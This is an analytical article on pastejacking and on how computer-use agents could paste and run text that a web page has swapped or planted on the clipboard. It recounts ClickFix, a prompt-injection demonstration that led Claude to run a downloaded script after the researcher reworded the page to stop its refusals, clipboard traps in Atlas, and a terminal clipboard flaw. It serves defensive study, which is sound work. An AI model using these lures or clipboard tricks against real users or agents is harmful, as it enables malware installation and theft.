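# Pastejacking and computer-use agents: when the pasted text is not the text that was copied

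## The clipboard, and how a web page can change what was copied

Pastejacking is an attack in which a web page puts text on a visitor's clipboard that the visitor did not choose to copy. When the visitor next pastes, they get the attacker's text instead of what they expected. The attack is about twenty years old, and for most of that time its victims were people. AI systems that operate desktops now copy and paste too. This raises the question of whether they are also vulnerable, and whether the defences that browser and terminal developers built for people still help when an agent pastes.

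Kohler and Lopez, in *Brewing Trouble*, describe a typical case from September 2025. Attackers had set up several copies of the website for Homebrew, a program that many Mac developers use to install other software. The real site shows a one-line install command, which readers copy and paste into a terminal, a window for running typed commands. The fake sites also showed a command, but a script stopped visitors from highlighting it, so they had to press a Copy button. The button put an extra command on the clipboard that the page did not show. Anyone who pasted the result got the Homebrew installer as well as malware, so they had little reason to suspect anything. The page also reported each press of the button to the attackers' server. On one fake site, the script still had a placeholder, with a comment in Russian marking where the malicious command should go. The operators filled it in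 before Kohler and Lopez published. The researchers infer that someone built the page as a service for other criminals.

### What the clipboard holds

The clipboard is the shared store in which an operating system keeps copied content for pasting. Unrelated programs can all read from it and write to it. W3C's *Clipboard API and events* (2026), the draft standard for how web pages use the clipboard, describes it as a list of items, each of which can hold several representations of the same content. A block of spreadsheet cells, for example, might be stored as a picture, an HTML table and plain text, and the program that receives the paste uses whichever form suits it.

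People don't normally see any of this. Most find out what the clipboard holds by pasting it. They assume the computer stored the text they highlighted, but a web page can make that assumption false in at least three ways.

### Hidden text, copy events and clicks

The oldest method uses a page's styling to hide text in the middle of a visible command. A reader who drags the mouse across the command also selects the hidden text, and the browser copies it all. ush.it's *User iteraction based exploitation*, an Italian security write-up from 2008, described this as "what you see is not what you copy". On Linux, the hidden text reached both the ordinary clipboard and a second one that fills as soon as the user highlights something. The method needs no script, so turning off JavaScript does not stop it, but ush.it pointed out that pasting into a plain text editor first reveals all the hidden text.

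Another method uses the copy event. When a user presses the copy shortcut, the browser notifies the page before it stores anything. If the page does nothing, the browser copies the selection. But a script on the page may supply its own data and cancel the default action, and the browser then stores the script's data instead. Web-based editors may need this feature to put their own formats on the clipboard. W3C illustrates it with a few lines of code that replace whatever the user copied with a greeting. The script in that example sets the plain text and the formatted text separately, and the two need not match, so one copy could in principle paste differently into a terminal and a word processor (an inference from the standard, not a reported attack). W3C discusses pages that tamper with copied data under the heading of nuisances, a mild term given that the altered text can be pasted into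 a terminal, and leaves it to browser makers to add restrictions if they want to.

In the remaining method, a script writes to the clipboard after a click, without a copy command from the user. The Copy buttons next to code samples work this way, and a malicious button makes the same call as a legitimate one but with different text. The script either passes a string directly to the browser's clipboard interface or, in an older technique, creates an invisible text field, selects its contents and triggers a copy. The fake Homebrew page contained both, with the older technique as a fallback. Browsers generally require a recent click or keypress first, but the click doesn't have to be on anything labelled "Copy".

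### Swapped text, planted text and clippers

W3C's security notes mention that page authors can change what a user copied, and that they can copy something the user never selected. These are two forms of pastejacking, and they need different defences.

In swapped text, the victim copies one visible string and the page substitutes another. Comparing the displayed string with the pasted one would reveal the attack. In planted text, the page writes to the clipboard after an unrelated click, with nothing selected. The victim has no expected string to compare with the pasted one, but the attacker must give the victim a reason to paste.

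Some of these techniques can produce either a swap or a plant. Hidden text produces a swap, because it is copied along with the text the user selects. A write after a click can produce either; the fake Homebrew button swapped text, while a script behind a checkbox plants it. Copy events can also be used for both, because the April draft from W3C (2016) allowed a script to fill the clipboard during a copy event even when the user had selected nothing.

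A clipper is malware already on a machine that replaces copied payment addresses with the attacker's. The person pasting may not be able to tell this from pastejacking, but a clipper does not need a web page, so rules about what web pages may do don't affect it.

A cruder attack is easy to confuse with these. Push Security found cloned installation pages, including one for Anthropic's coding assistant Claude Code, on which attackers had edited the visible instructions. The reader sees the malicious command, copies it and pastes it unchanged. This is not pastejacking, and a check that the pasted text matches the displayed text would not catch it.

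### From hidden text to ClickFix

ush.it described its discovery as already two years old when it published in 2008, which puts the hidden-text trick at about 2006. What prompted publication was a run of attacks that used Flash, a browser plug-in of the time. In August of that year SonicWall's *Flash ads hijack cliboard* (2008) reported that banner ads on legitimate sites, among them Newsweek, Digg and MSNBC.com, were loading a malicious link into visitors' clipboards. The link led to a fake antivirus program, and the attackers were counting on people to paste it into emails and blog comments without looking. This was planted text, in the wild, years before the word pastejacking existed.

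MajorGeeks' *Old tricks are new again* (2013), a repost of an article from the technology site The H, noted that several websites were demonstrating hidden text again and that Linux users were most at risk, because so many of their how-to guides consist of commands to paste.

Browsers then began letting scripts copy text without Flash. Frontend Focus' *Clipboard Hijacking with HTML5* (2015) objected that Chrome 43 allowed this without asking the user's permission. The post's demonstration, built in a few minutes, put nonsense on the clipboard when a reader highlighted some text and released the mouse button. On desktop Chrome the highlighting then disappeared, which might have alerted the reader, but another developer soon produced a version that kept the text selected. The post also mentions a milder practice that most readers will have seen, in which newspaper sites add a link or an advertisement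 to copied text.

Dylan Ayrey, a developer and security researcher, gave the attack its name. Ecosyste.ms, an index of open-source projects, dates his repository to 17 May 2016 and quotes his description of it as "a demo of overriding what's in a person's clipboard". The security press covered it within days. In *Pastejacking attack relies on your clipboard as an attack vector*, Paganini (2016) acknowledged that HTML and CSS versions had existed for a long time. Ayrey's version was new because it used JavaScript. In SecurityWeek's *Pastejacking Attack Allows Hackers to Execute Malicious Code*, he explains that a script can replace the copied text after an event, or on a short timer following it, and can more easily insert unusual characters that exploit the text editor Vim. The victim also no longer had to select particular text, since the script replaced anything they copied from the page.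 The demonstration worked only when the victim copied with the keyboard, and it failed in Safari.

Planted text has since become the more prominent form through ClickFix, a scam in which a page plants a command on the clipboard and tells the visitor to paste and run it. Group-IB has tracked ClickFix since August 2024 and describes the usual lure as a fake verification prompt. In one campaign that Unit 42 analysed, the visitor ticks a box to prove they are human, which triggers a script that writes a command to the clipboard. A pop-up then tells them to finish the check by opening the Windows Run dialog, pasting, and running what appears. The command installs a program that steals information from the machine.

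Eric Lawrence, who works on Microsoft's Defender security product, lists the technique in text/plain's *Attack Techniques* among attacks he calls "so stupid, they can't possibly succeed", though he says they do succeed. He also describes an earlier version from around 2011, in which scammers persuaded Facebook users to paste script into the browser's address bar. According to *User Execution* (2025), an entry in MITRE ATT&CK, a widely used catalogue of attack methods, ClickFix succeeds partly because a command that victims run themselves may bypass email filters and the browser's sandbox. Microsoft (2025) reports that the technique became more popular over the preceding year, and Microsoft (2026) describes a shift on Macs from disk images that victims install by hand to commands that they paste into Terminal.

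Security firms use the name ClickFix loosely. Recorded Future's *ClickFix Campaigns Targeting Windows and macOS* includes cases in which victims copy the command by hand and nothing reaches the clipboard automatically. *Fake Homebrew Typosquats Used to Deliver Cuckoo Stealer via ClickFix* uses the name for a Copy button that silently swaps in a malicious command. A count of ClickFix incidents can therefore include some in which the page did not plant any text on the clipboard.

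### Why terminals and payment addresses

In a letter or a chat window, a wrong paste is usually just embarrassing, and the writer sees it and deletes it. A terminal, however, runs text as commands with the user's own permissions. Normally a pasted command runs only after the user presses Enter, but an unprotected terminal treats a line break in pasted text as a press of Enter. If the pasted text ends in a line break, the command runs at once, before the user can read it. Some terminals now warn about this.

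Reading the screen afterwards may not help either. SecurityWeek reports that one version of Ayrey's demonstration ran its own command, cleared the terminal and then displayed the command the user had meant to copy. On Linux, according to MajorGeeks, the attacker's command may also run with administrator rights if the user has recently entered a password for sudo, the tool that grants them.

These attacks are easier because people are used to pasting commands from web pages into a terminal. The real instructions for Homebrew and Claude Code both involve doing this. Push Security notes that the recommended command for Claude Code, like those for many similar tools, fetches a script from a remote server and runs it immediately. Someone who inspects such a command before pressing Enter can see where the script comes from but not what it does. To spot a malicious version, they would have to know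 the correct web address and notice that this one was different.

A payment address is dangerous for other reasons. An Ethereum address, a common kind of cryptocurrency address, is "0x" followed by 40 hexadecimal digits. It has no readable meaning, and a person comparing two of them will probably look at only a few characters at each end. An attacker can therefore generate addresses until one has the right ends. Matching the first four digits and the last four takes about 16⁸ attempts on average, or 4.3 billion, which ordinary hardware can easily do. Many address formats include checksums to catch typing errors, but these don't catch the substitution because the attacker's address is also valid. Once the network has confirmed the transfer, no bank can reverse it. However, pasting an address into a form doesn't send the money. Someone still has to press Send, which leaves time to check the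 address, whereas a line break pasted into a terminal runs the command immediately.

### The agent's loop

A computer-use agent is an AI system that operates a computer through screenshots, clicks and keystrokes. The software around the model, known as the harness, takes a screenshot and passes it to the model along with the user's task. The model chooses an action, such as clicking at certain coordinates or pressing the paste shortcut. The harness carries out the action and takes a new screenshot, and the loop repeats until the task is finished. To move an install command from a browser to a terminal, the agent can press the page's Copy button and paste, or it can read the command off the screen and type it, which does not use the clipboard. It follows from this loop that if the agent pastes, a command swapped in by an attacker can pass from the page to the clipboard to the terminal without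 the model reading it. The attack can therefore work without prompt injection, meaning text in outside content that an AI system follows as if it were an instruction from its user. A ClickFix attack would depend on prompt injection, because the agent would have to obey the instructions on the screen before the planted command could do any harm.

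## What the design of desktop agents implies about the attack

People nearly always copy and paste a command to move it from a web page to a terminal. Agents have other methods, some of which don't use the clipboard. Developers' documentation and open-source code show which methods agents can use and what the model can see during each one. This is enough to infer where pastejacking should work against an agent, but not how often it would.

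### Four routes from a page to another program

An agent can read a command in a screenshot and retype it with a typing action that contains the whole string. Anthropic's *Computer use tool*, the developer documentation for Claude's desktop control, lists 17 actions, including one that types literal text wherever the keyboard focus is and one that zooms in on part of the screen so that Claude can read small print. Because the agent copies nothing, the page has no copy to tamper with. The risk is that the agent misreads a character, which usually produces an error in a command and will often make a payment address fail its checksum.

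Some harnesses also give the model the page's text directly. OpenAI offers developers browser tools for tasks that involve reading page text, and Cua's *All tools*, the reference for an open-source desktop driver, lists several that read a page's text or inspect its elements. The agent finds the string in that text and types it into the other program. Hidden text could still get in, because a tool that extracts the page's text will probably include text that is invisible but selectable. But the model would then receive the hidden part as extra characters in a string that it has to read (an inference).

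A desktop agent copies and pastes text much as a person does. It triple-clicks or drags across the command, presses the copy shortcut, switches windows and presses the paste shortcut. Anthropic's tool accepts key combinations, and Playwright's *Keyboard & Mouse*, the documentation for a browser automation tool that agents can use, lists Control+C and Control+V among the common ones. Because a desktop harness sends ordinary keyboard and mouse input, the browser presumably treats the agent's copy as the user's and fires the same copy event on the page that W3C describes.

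The remaining route is the site's own Copy button. A model may well choose it because it takes one click on an easy target, while dragging across a long command takes two accurate positions. The button also gives the page the most control, since the page's script supplies the entire string.

When an agent retypes a string or takes it from the page's text, the model writes out every character. A malicious command would therefore have to appear in the model's output, where its safety training or a filter in the harness might stop it. When the agent copies and pastes, the model outputs only the keyboard shortcut, not the pasted text.

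An agent may not need any of this to run an install command. Anthropic's sample setup includes a separate tool for running shell commands, which Claude typically uses alongside the desktop controls. An agent with that tool can run the command without opening a terminal window. The tool doesn't help with a payment form in a browser or a wallet program, where the agent has to type or paste the address into the field.

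### Harnesses that paste when the model types

A model that retypes a string may still use the clipboard, because the harness determines how a typing action is carried out. The PyPI page for *ui-tars* describes a Python package that converts the output of vision models into automation scripts. These scripts enter text by pasting it by default, though a setting can change this.

Glama's *type_text*, a directory page, reproduces a function from the open-source tool mac-use-mcp. The function saves the clipboard's text, replaces it with the model's text, presses Command+V, waits briefly and restores the old text. It then reports success and the text's length to the model. That length comes from the string the model supplied, so it would be the same if different text had been pasted.

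Other harnesses avoid the clipboard. Google's sample code for its Gemini models sends keystrokes, and Cua's typing tool on macOS inserts text through the operating system's accessibility interface. Anthropic leaves the implementation to the developer. The model sends the same kind of request in each case and may receive nothing that indicates which method the harness uses.

Entering text through the clipboard exposes it to other programs, but mostly not to pastejacking, because the harness writes its own string just before it pastes, overwriting anything a web page stored earlier. A clipper already on the machine could replace a payment address in the short gap between the write and the paste. A person using the same desktop could also overwrite the text by copying something during that gap. Alibaba Cloud's *Paste into window*, the documentation for a conventional automation tool, advises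 against clipboard entry when a user is also interacting with the machine.

Restoring the old clipboard contents creates two more problems. If a page has planted text on the clipboard, mac-use-mcp saves it, types something else and then puts the planted text back, ready for a later paste. And if the receiving program is slow and reads the clipboard only after the harness has restored it, the planted text would arrive in place of the model's text. Both problems are inferred from the order of steps in the code, not from reported attacks. Simular's *Class*, a reference page for another agent's clipboard functions, describes a similar routine that also verifies that the clipboard holds the right string before pasting. That check gives a clipper less time to swap the string, but it doesn't stop the routine from restoring planted text.

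### Four conditions for harm

For swapped text to do damage, four things have to happen:

1. The string travels by clipboard.
2. The page changes it.
3. Nobody notices before the committing action, meaning the keypress or click after which the pasted text takes effect.
4. The agent takes that action.

"Nobody" includes the model, a person watching the screen and any check in the harness. The attack fails if any one condition fails. An agent that retypes the command breaks the first condition, and an agent that reads the terminal before pressing Enter can break the third.

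An agent gets little warning from the screen that the second condition holds, because a screenshot doesn't show the clipboard. None of Anthropic's 17 actions reads the clipboard, and none of the actions OpenAI lists for its computer tool does either. Some harnesses do provide a way to read it. One is agent-desktop, a command-line tool for agents, which gives an example of checking the clipboard between copying and pasting. Without such a function, an agent can still paste into an empty text document and look at the result.

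It is also hard to tell from a Copy button's appearance what clicking it will do. *A Systematization of Security Vulnerabilities in Computer Use Agents* (2025) describes a related case in which researchers placed a button labelled "Enter the blog" over a hidden form. OpenAI's Operator agent, asked to enter the blog and summarise a post, clicked the only button it could see and triggered a simulated payment. A misleading Copy button also does something other than what its label says, but the click does no damage by itself. The agent still has to paste, and pasting usually puts the string where the model can see it.

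### An install command, step by step

Suppose a user asks an agent to install a developer tool, and the agent lands on a cloned download page like the fake Homebrew sites.

| What happens | What the model can see |
|---|---|
| The agent opens the page | The genuine command, with a Copy button beside it |
| It clicks Copy, and the page's script stores a different command | An acknowledgement that the click went through; in a new screenshot, perhaps a "Copied" label drawn by the page |
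| It switches to the terminal and pastes | Nothing new until the next screenshot, which shows the substituted command at the prompt |
| It presses Enter, and the command runs | The command's output, or whatever the command leaves on the screen |

The agent can best catch the swap after pasting the command and before pressing Enter. By then the model has seen both the string on the web page and the one in the terminal, and only needs to compare them. Terminal text may be small, and Anthropic recommends modest screen resolutions, so the model might have to zoom in. A long command can also wrap over several lines or run past the edge of the window.

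The earlier screenshot may no longer be available for comparison, because developers sometimes remove old screenshots to save space on long tasks. Anthropic suggests that those who do so keep the last three and prune every 25 turns, though it advises against client-side pruning on its newest models. Copying and pasting usually take only a few turns, so pruning would rarely matter unless the agent did something else in between.

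Looking at the screen after pressing Enter is much less useful, because the command has already run and its output may look right. The fake Homebrew button added malware to the real installer, so a model that checked for Homebrew afterward would find it installed.

If the swapped text ends in a line break, a terminal without paste protection runs it as soon as the agent pastes it. Even an agent that takes a screenshot after every action sees the text only after the command has run.

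### A payment address, step by step

Suppose the user asks the agent to pay an invoice in Ethereum. The invoice page shows an address, and the model can read all 42 characters in a screenshot. When the agent clicks the copy icon, the page puts the attacker's address on the clipboard. Its first four and last four digits match those of the displayed address. The model receives only confirmation that its click went through.

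The agent opens the wallet and pastes. The next screenshot shows the attacker's address in the recipient field, possibly cut short if the field is narrow. The agent enters the amount and clicks Send. If the wallet asks for confirmation, the model sees the address again, perhaps still shortened.

The model has more chances to check a pasted address than a pasted terminal command, because the agent normally has to fill in the amount before it can send anything. But a substituted address is harder to recognise, because nothing in it stands out as an unfamiliar web address might in a command. If the attacker used trial and error to generate an address that matches the original at both ends, about 30 of the 32 digits in between would differ. A model could hardly miss the difference if it compared the full strings, but it would not notice if it checked only the ends.

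An attacker who controls the whole page could display their own address, so even an agent that retyped it would pay the wrong person. Swapping the address during copying is useful when someone might check the displayed one, such as the site's owner or a user who already knows it. If the user put the correct address in the request, the agent can type it from there and has no reason to trust the page.

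### Batch actions

Both examples assume that the model gets a screenshot between pasting and committing. Many harnesses let the model skip that screenshot by batching actions, which means it issues several in one response and the harness runs them in order. A batch might click in the terminal, paste, press Enter and take a screenshot. The model would then see what it had pasted only after the command had started.

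Anthropic says Claude typically ends a batch with a screenshot, which helps it plan the next step but comes too late to stop an action in the current batch. Anthropic also tells developers to stop a batch when an action fails. Pasting the wrong text does not count as a failure, since the harness pressed the right keys. Where a human has to approve consequential actions, however, Anthropic tells developers to ask before each action runs, because a batch can complete a multistep action in one turn.

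Other developers also group actions. OpenAI's *Computer use* describes a loop in which the application runs every action the model has returned before capturing the screen. For GPT-6 Astra, OpenAI recommends having the model write code to operate the interface, which lets one call combine actions with loops and conditions. In its sample tool description, OpenAI tells the model to check the screen "after a short group of actions", and such a group could include both paste and Enter. Cua calls its tool for running several actions together "the default way to act".

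An older Google action could type text and press Enter in the same step. In Google's sample code, the model writes the text and the harness enters it as keystrokes. This is less dangerous than a batch that pastes and presses Enter, which submits text the model may never have seen.

Even an agent that takes one action at a time may not see the pasted text before it presses Enter. Anthropic lets developers limit Claude to a single action per turn, but the harness can respond to a keypress with just "OK" and no image. Claude then sees the result only if it requests a screenshot or the developer attaches one. Google's loop returns a new screenshot after each turn's actions have run, so a model that pastes in one turn and presses Enter in the next receives an image of the pasted text in between. According to Cua's documentation, the agent should observe again and check whenever the driver cannot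 confirm an action's effect.

Screenshots can also go out of date before the agent acts. *Temporal UI State Inconsistency in Desktop GUI Agents* (2026) describes attacks in which malware on the same desktop exploits this delay to redirect an agent's next click. Swapping copied text doesn't require such precise timing, because the altered string can stay on the clipboard for minutes.

### Swapped text is not prompt injection

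When a page swaps the copied text, the agent still follows only its user's instructions, such as to install a program or pay an invoice. It fails because one piece of data is false: the clipboard doesn't hold the text the page displayed, but the agent assumes it does.

*AutoRedClaw* (2026), a paper on automated attack testing for agents, puts this kind of error in a category called "Clipboard and Dataflow Confusion". It locates the failure in the relationship between where data comes from, what it contains and where it goes. This fits swapped text well because the web page shows a legitimate command and the terminal accepts commands. Each screen can look normal on its own even though the string changed on the way.

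Defences against prompt injection therefore have little to detect. Anthropic runs classifiers over screenshots and other tool results to look for injected instructions, and Google offers a similar optional scan. A page that swaps text can display only the genuine command and a Copy button. After the paste, a screenshot may show a malicious command, but that command is input for the terminal and does not instruct the model. A classifier might still flag it, although detecting malicious commands is not the task Anthropic describes.

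*A Survey on Agentic Security* (2025) similarly places attacks that arrive through an interface "outside the reach of prompt-level defenses". It discusses attacks on what agents perceive, such as deceptive buttons, but the reasoning extends to a button with a hidden effect on the clipboard.

Filters on typed commands can also miss pasted ones. Nous Research's *Computer Use*, the documentation for the open-source Hermes Agent, lists patterns that the agent may not type, including a download piped into a shell. A filter that checks only typed text would miss the same command pasted from the clipboard, because the model sends only the paste shortcut. The filter could even push agents towards pasting, the riskier option, because many legitimate install commands have this form and an agent blocked from typing one might still be able to paste it. Hermes asks for approval before keypresses by default,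 but the paste shortcut doesn't show the person approving it what will be pasted.

A harmless request does not make the task safe either. In *The Blind Spot of Agent Safety*, Ding, Zhai and colleagues (2026) gave agents 300 desktop tasks in which the user's instruction was benign and the danger came from the environment or from carrying out the task. In 73% of the tasks, Claude 4.5 Sonnet, now an old model, caused harm in at least one of three attempts. The task categories include phishing sites and malware but not clipboard tampering, so the figure is not an estimate for swapped text. They also found that safety training rarely took effect after the first few steps. A swapped command appears several steps into an ordinary job, so this finding suggests the model would be less likely to object to it.

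Planted text could plausibly also work without prompt injection. Suppose a page puts a command on the clipboard when the agent dismisses a cookie notice, and the agent later tries to copy something else but selects nothing. The copy fails without any visible sign, so the next paste inserts the planted command. This is an inference from how the clipboard works, and it would require a coincidence that an attacker could not easily arrange.

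### What the designs leave open

The four conditions multiply, which makes it easy to see what a risk estimate would require. Take 100 tasks, with invented numbers throughout. The agent uses the clipboard in 60 of them. Every page swaps the text, so it pastes 60 altered strings. It notices a third of the swaps, or 20, and stops. In the other 40 it goes on to press Enter or Send:

100 × 0.60 × 1 × ⅔ × 1 = 40 harmful outcomes

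Most real pages do not tamper with copied text, so a far smaller share of everyday tasks would end in harm. Setting the probability of tampering to 1 isolates the agent's behaviour on a malicious page. In this calculation, the number of harmful outcomes would fall to 20 if the agent either used the clipboard half as often or missed half as many swaps.

Documentation cannot establish either of those rates. A list of actions shows that an agent can copy and paste, but not how often it does so when it could retype the string or use a shell. That choice probably varies with the model, the length of the string and the other tools available. How often the agent looks at the pasted text before committing it is just as uncertain. Anthropic warns that Claude sometimes assumes an action has succeeded without checking the result, and suggests a prompt that makes it take a screenshot and evaluate the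 outcome after each step. Developers therefore cannot assume that the model will check, but the warning doesn't specify how often it fails to.

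## Demonstrations against deployed agents

Security researchers have published at least two demonstrations of clipboard attacks on AI agents, one against Claude in May 2025 and one against OpenAI's Atlas browser that October. A third report, from 2026, describes a terminal program in which text printed on the screen could overwrite the clipboard. All three describe researchers' own tests, and none reports a victim.

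### A planted command and Claude

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who blogs as Embrace The Red, tested how an AI system would handle a ClickFix page and presented the result at a workshop in San Francisco on 15 May 2025. He tested Claude 3.7 Sonnet, a model Anthropic had released that February, as it operated a desktop with a Linux terminal.

Embrace The Red's *AI ClickFix* describes a web page that Rehberger made to trick Claude into running a command. ChatGPT wrote most of the page, which showed a fake verification prompt with a button. When Claude clicked the button, a script put a command on the clipboard, and the page displayed instructions to open a terminal, paste and press Enter. Rehberger included a picture of the terminal's icon to help Claude find it. Claude followed the instructions, and the command downloaded a script from Rehberger's server and ran it. The script only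 opened the Calculator app, but a real attacker could have run anything the user's account allowed.

Claude sometimes refused at first. Rehberger suspected that the page looked too much like a CAPTCHA, a test meant to keep bots out, which he says Claude is trained to hand back to the user. After he changed a few words on the page and its button to make it look less like one, the refusals almost disappeared. If he was right, Claude had refused because of its training on CAPTCHAs, not because it recognised an attack. Rehberger says that the attack reproduced well and that nearly all his variations worked, but he gives no count of attempts or refusals.

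In a variation that didn't use the clipboard, Rehberger displayed the command as ordinary text and asked Claude to type it into the terminal. He says this also worked "pretty well". Claude's safety training could have led it to refuse to type the command, but it mostly complied. Perhaps this was because the command looked like a genuine install command, though that explanation is an inference.

The attack therefore needed an agent that would follow a web page's instructions, but it did not need the clipboard. Rehberger attributes it to prompt injection. Planting the command on the clipboard still helps the attacker, because no screenshot shows the command before the agent pastes it. Rehberger's instructions also combined pasting and pressing Enter in a single step, so Claude may have run the command without looking at it. It is doubtful that looking would have helped, since the attack also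 worked when Claude typed the command itself.

MITRE's *ATLAS* (2020), a catalogue of attacks on AI systems that is unrelated to OpenAI's browser, added the test on 31 March 2026. It labels the case an "Exercise", as it does other researchers' tests, and reserves "Incident" for real attacks. In the first three of the entry's eight steps, the researcher gets access to ChatGPT, builds the page and the script, and puts them online. In the other five, the agent visits the page, takes the bait, reads the injected instructions and carries them out, and then the script runs.

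MITRE classifies the instructions as indirect prompt injection and the bait as "AI Agent Clickbait". MITRE's *AI Agent Clickbait* defines this bait as deceptive web content that lures agents into unintended actions, and gives copying code as an example. No step in the entry is specific to the clipboard, and the planting, the paste and the press of Enter all fall under the agent's use of its tools. This fits the evidence, since the typed variation would involve much the same steps.

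### A planted link in the Atlas browser

OpenAI launched ChatGPT Atlas, a browser with an agent mode that can click and type on web pages, on 21 October 2025. The next day, a hacker known as Pliny the Liberator posted a video of a clipboard attack on it. According to Android Authority's *OpenAI's Atlas browser has a security flaw* (2025), he had modified his own website so that every button put a phishing link on the visitor's clipboard. When the agent clicked a button, it put the link on the user's clipboard without the user's knowledge.

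The harm would come later, when the user, rather than the agent, pastes the link. In Pliny's example, the user opens a new tab, pastes into the address bar and lands on a fake site. Nolan (2025), in *Cybersecurity experts warn OpenAI’s ChatGPT Atlas is vulnerable to attacks*, adds that the site could steal login details, including multifactor authentication codes. Android Authority overstates the danger when it warns that a user is compromised at the next paste. Pasting the link into a document does nothing by itself, and on a fake login page the user still has to enter a password.

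Pliny says the agent can usually see the text that passes between it and the user, and is trained to recognise prompt injections. But the page's script does the copying, so the agent has "zero awareness" of what it has put on the clipboard. Nolan groups the demonstration with prompt injection attacks, though by Pliny's account the agent only had to click a button, not obey any hostile text. Pliny says the copying code is in the site's "backend", but a script has to run in the visitor's browser to reach the clipboard. The browser could therefore in principle detect the write and warn the agent or the user (an inference).

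The attack is worse if the user has already copied something. Suppose they copy a bank account number, ask the agent to look something up, and then paste. If the agent clicked a button on a malicious page during the lookup, the attacker's text will have replaced the number. The user could notice by comparing the pasted text with the original, but they have little reason to check because they never visited the page themselves. This scenario is inferred from the fact that the user and the agent share a clipboard, though Pliny also mentions banking and data entry among the activities at risk.

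When Nolan asked OpenAI for comment, the company referred her to a post on X by Dane Stuckey, its chief information security officer. Stuckey called prompt injection an unsolved problem and described OpenAI's work against it. He also described logged-out mode, which keeps the agent away from the user's credentials, and Watch Mode, which pauses the agent on sensitive sites if the user leaves the tab.

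Neither feature would obviously help here. The user pastes the link in their own session, possibly long after the agent has finished, and someone watching the agent would see only a click on an ordinary button. Willison (2025), in *Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT Atlas*, also had trouble getting Watch Mode to start on GitHub and a banking site, where the agent continued after he switched to another application.

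OpenAI announced a security update for Atlas on 22 December 2025. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) explains that OpenAI had trained an AI attacker to search for prompt injections, then trained the browser's agent to resist the ones it found. In one of these attacks, a malicious email made the agent send the user's resignation to their chief executive instead of drafting an out-of-office reply. Such training teaches an agent to ignore hostile instructions, but Pliny's trapped buttons did not depend on such instructions. Neither Stuckey's post nor the December announcement mentions the clipboard. OpenAI may have fixed the problem without announcing it, but there is no public record of a specific fix.

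### Terminal output that overwrites the clipboard

Pages like Rehberger's and Pliny's need a click to plant text on the clipboard. In Warp, a terminal program designed for working with AI agents, displaying certain output was enough to do so.

Terminals act on control codes in the text they display, such as codes that move the cursor or change colours. One code, OSC 52, can read or write the system clipboard, which lets users copy text from an editor on a remote machine, for example. Pelaseyed (2026) reports in *When Terminal Output Owns Your Clipboard* that Warp executed this code from any source without asking the user. A remote server, a local program or a web page that an agent fetched into the terminal could therefore replace a copied command or wallet address before the user pasted it.

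The same code could make Warp hand over whatever was on the clipboard, such as a password. Pelaseyed considers this more serious than the overwriting.

INCIBE's *CVE-2026-48725* (2026), a public vulnerability database entry, rates the flaw's severity at 8.1 out of 10. Judging by the version numbers, the flaw was present from April 2021 until a release on 6 May 2026, seven weeks before the entry appeared. The fix adds a setting that blocks clipboard access by default.

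Pelaseyed's team used computer use as a testing method in this case, to operate the real Mac app, display crafted output and watch the clipboard change. He doesn't describe a test in which an agent then pasted the altered text. He points out that in a terminal with AI agents, output can come from the model or from any tool or page it relays, and all of it had the same access to the clipboard.

This attack needed no web page, so it is not pastejacking in the strict sense, and browser restrictions would not have stopped it. A clipper also works without a web page but requires malware on the machine, whereas this attack required only that a Warp user display output the attacker controlled.

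### The case that is still missing

| | Claude, May 2025 | Atlas, October 2025 | Warp, 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|
| What changed the clipboard | A page's script, after the agent clicked | A page's script, after the agent clicked | A control code in terminal output |
| Who pastes | The agent | The user, later | Nobody in the reported test |
| Did the attack rely on prompt injection? | Yes | No | No |
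| Demonstrated result | A harmless script ran | A phishing link reached the clipboard | Terminal output read and overwrote the clipboard |
| Reported victims | None | None | None |

No agent in these cases copied a string its user wanted and then pasted a different one. As of December 2026, there seems to be no published demonstration of that attack. *AutoRedClaw* describes something close to it. Its category for clipboard confusion includes hidden content that travels with visible data, and it suggests varying what remains from an earlier transfer. These are guidelines for generating tests, and they don't show that an agent has failed one.

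Guardio's *Scamlexity* describes PromptFix, another attack that adapts ClickFix to AI browsers. It takes control of the agent through instructions hidden in a fake CAPTCHA, so it doesn't demonstrate pastejacking either.

The two agent demonstrations show that some of the steps a swap requires are possible. In both, a page wrote to the clipboard after an agent clicked. Claude also pasted into a terminal and pressed Enter. But Claude used the clipboard because the page told it to, so the test doesn't show whether an agent would do so on its own. It also doesn't show whether an agent would notice a substitution, because the page displayed no command for Claude to compare with the one it pasted.

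There also seems to be no published retest of Rehberger's page on a 2026 model, but related attacks have continued to work on newer agents. In *Agent Data Injection*, Choi describes how a fake product review made three web agents click buttons their users didn't intend them to click. When a user asked Claude for Chrome to summarise the reviews on a page, it ordered a product, and the attack still worked with Claude Opus 4.8.

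Zenity Labs' *Grand Theft Atlas* calls Atlas the most hardened agentic browser its researchers have tested. Atlas blocks certain pages and asks for confirmation before sensitive actions, but a comment planted under a post on X still made it send phishing messages from the victim's WhatsApp account. Neither attack used the clipboard, but both make it unsafe to assume newer agents would ignore a page like Rehberger's.

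### How much one demonstration can establish

A successful demonstration proves that an attack is possible with a particular model, harness and page. It refutes the claim that agents are immune, but gives little evidence of how often the attack works. If an attack succeeds on 5% of attempts, a researcher who tries it 20 times has a 64% chance of at least one success (1 − 0.95²⁰ ≈ 0.64), and a video of that success would look the same as one of an attack that works every time.

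Rehberger's comment that refusals were rare suggests a high success rate, but the rate can't be estimated without counts. Even ten successes in ten attempts would be compatible with a true rate of about 74%, since an attack with that rate has a 5% chance of succeeding ten times in a row (0.74¹⁰ ≈ 0.05).

He also revised his page until Claude mostly stopped refusing. Real attackers can do the same, so this is a reasonable way to find out what a determined attacker could achieve, but a poor way to estimate how an agent would respond to an average malicious page. A small change in wording had a large effect on Claude's refusals, so results from one page may not carry over to another, let alone to a different model.

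The lack of a demonstration is also weak evidence that agents can resist swapped text. Researchers may not have tried the attack, or may have tried it, failed and not published the result. A safe test would not be hard to build. A page could show a real install command next to a Copy button that stores a different but harmless one, and a user could ask the agent to install the program. For each run, the researcher would record whether the agent used the button, selected the text, retyped it or ran the command through a separate shell tool, and whether it took a screenshot between pasting and pressing Enter. Runs in which the button stores the displayed command would show how often the agent stops or fails for unrelated reasons.

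## Controlled experiments with agents

No published experiment seems to measure how often an agent pastes swapped text and runs it. Several studies from 2025 and 2026 come close to testing one part of the problem, such as whether agents act on false data or run code they haven't read. Most report an attack success rate, the share of test cases in which the attacker achieves their goal. That rate depends heavily on what the researchers let the attacker do and how they chose the cases, so the figures below don't directly apply to pastejacking.

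### A benchmark with a clipboard category

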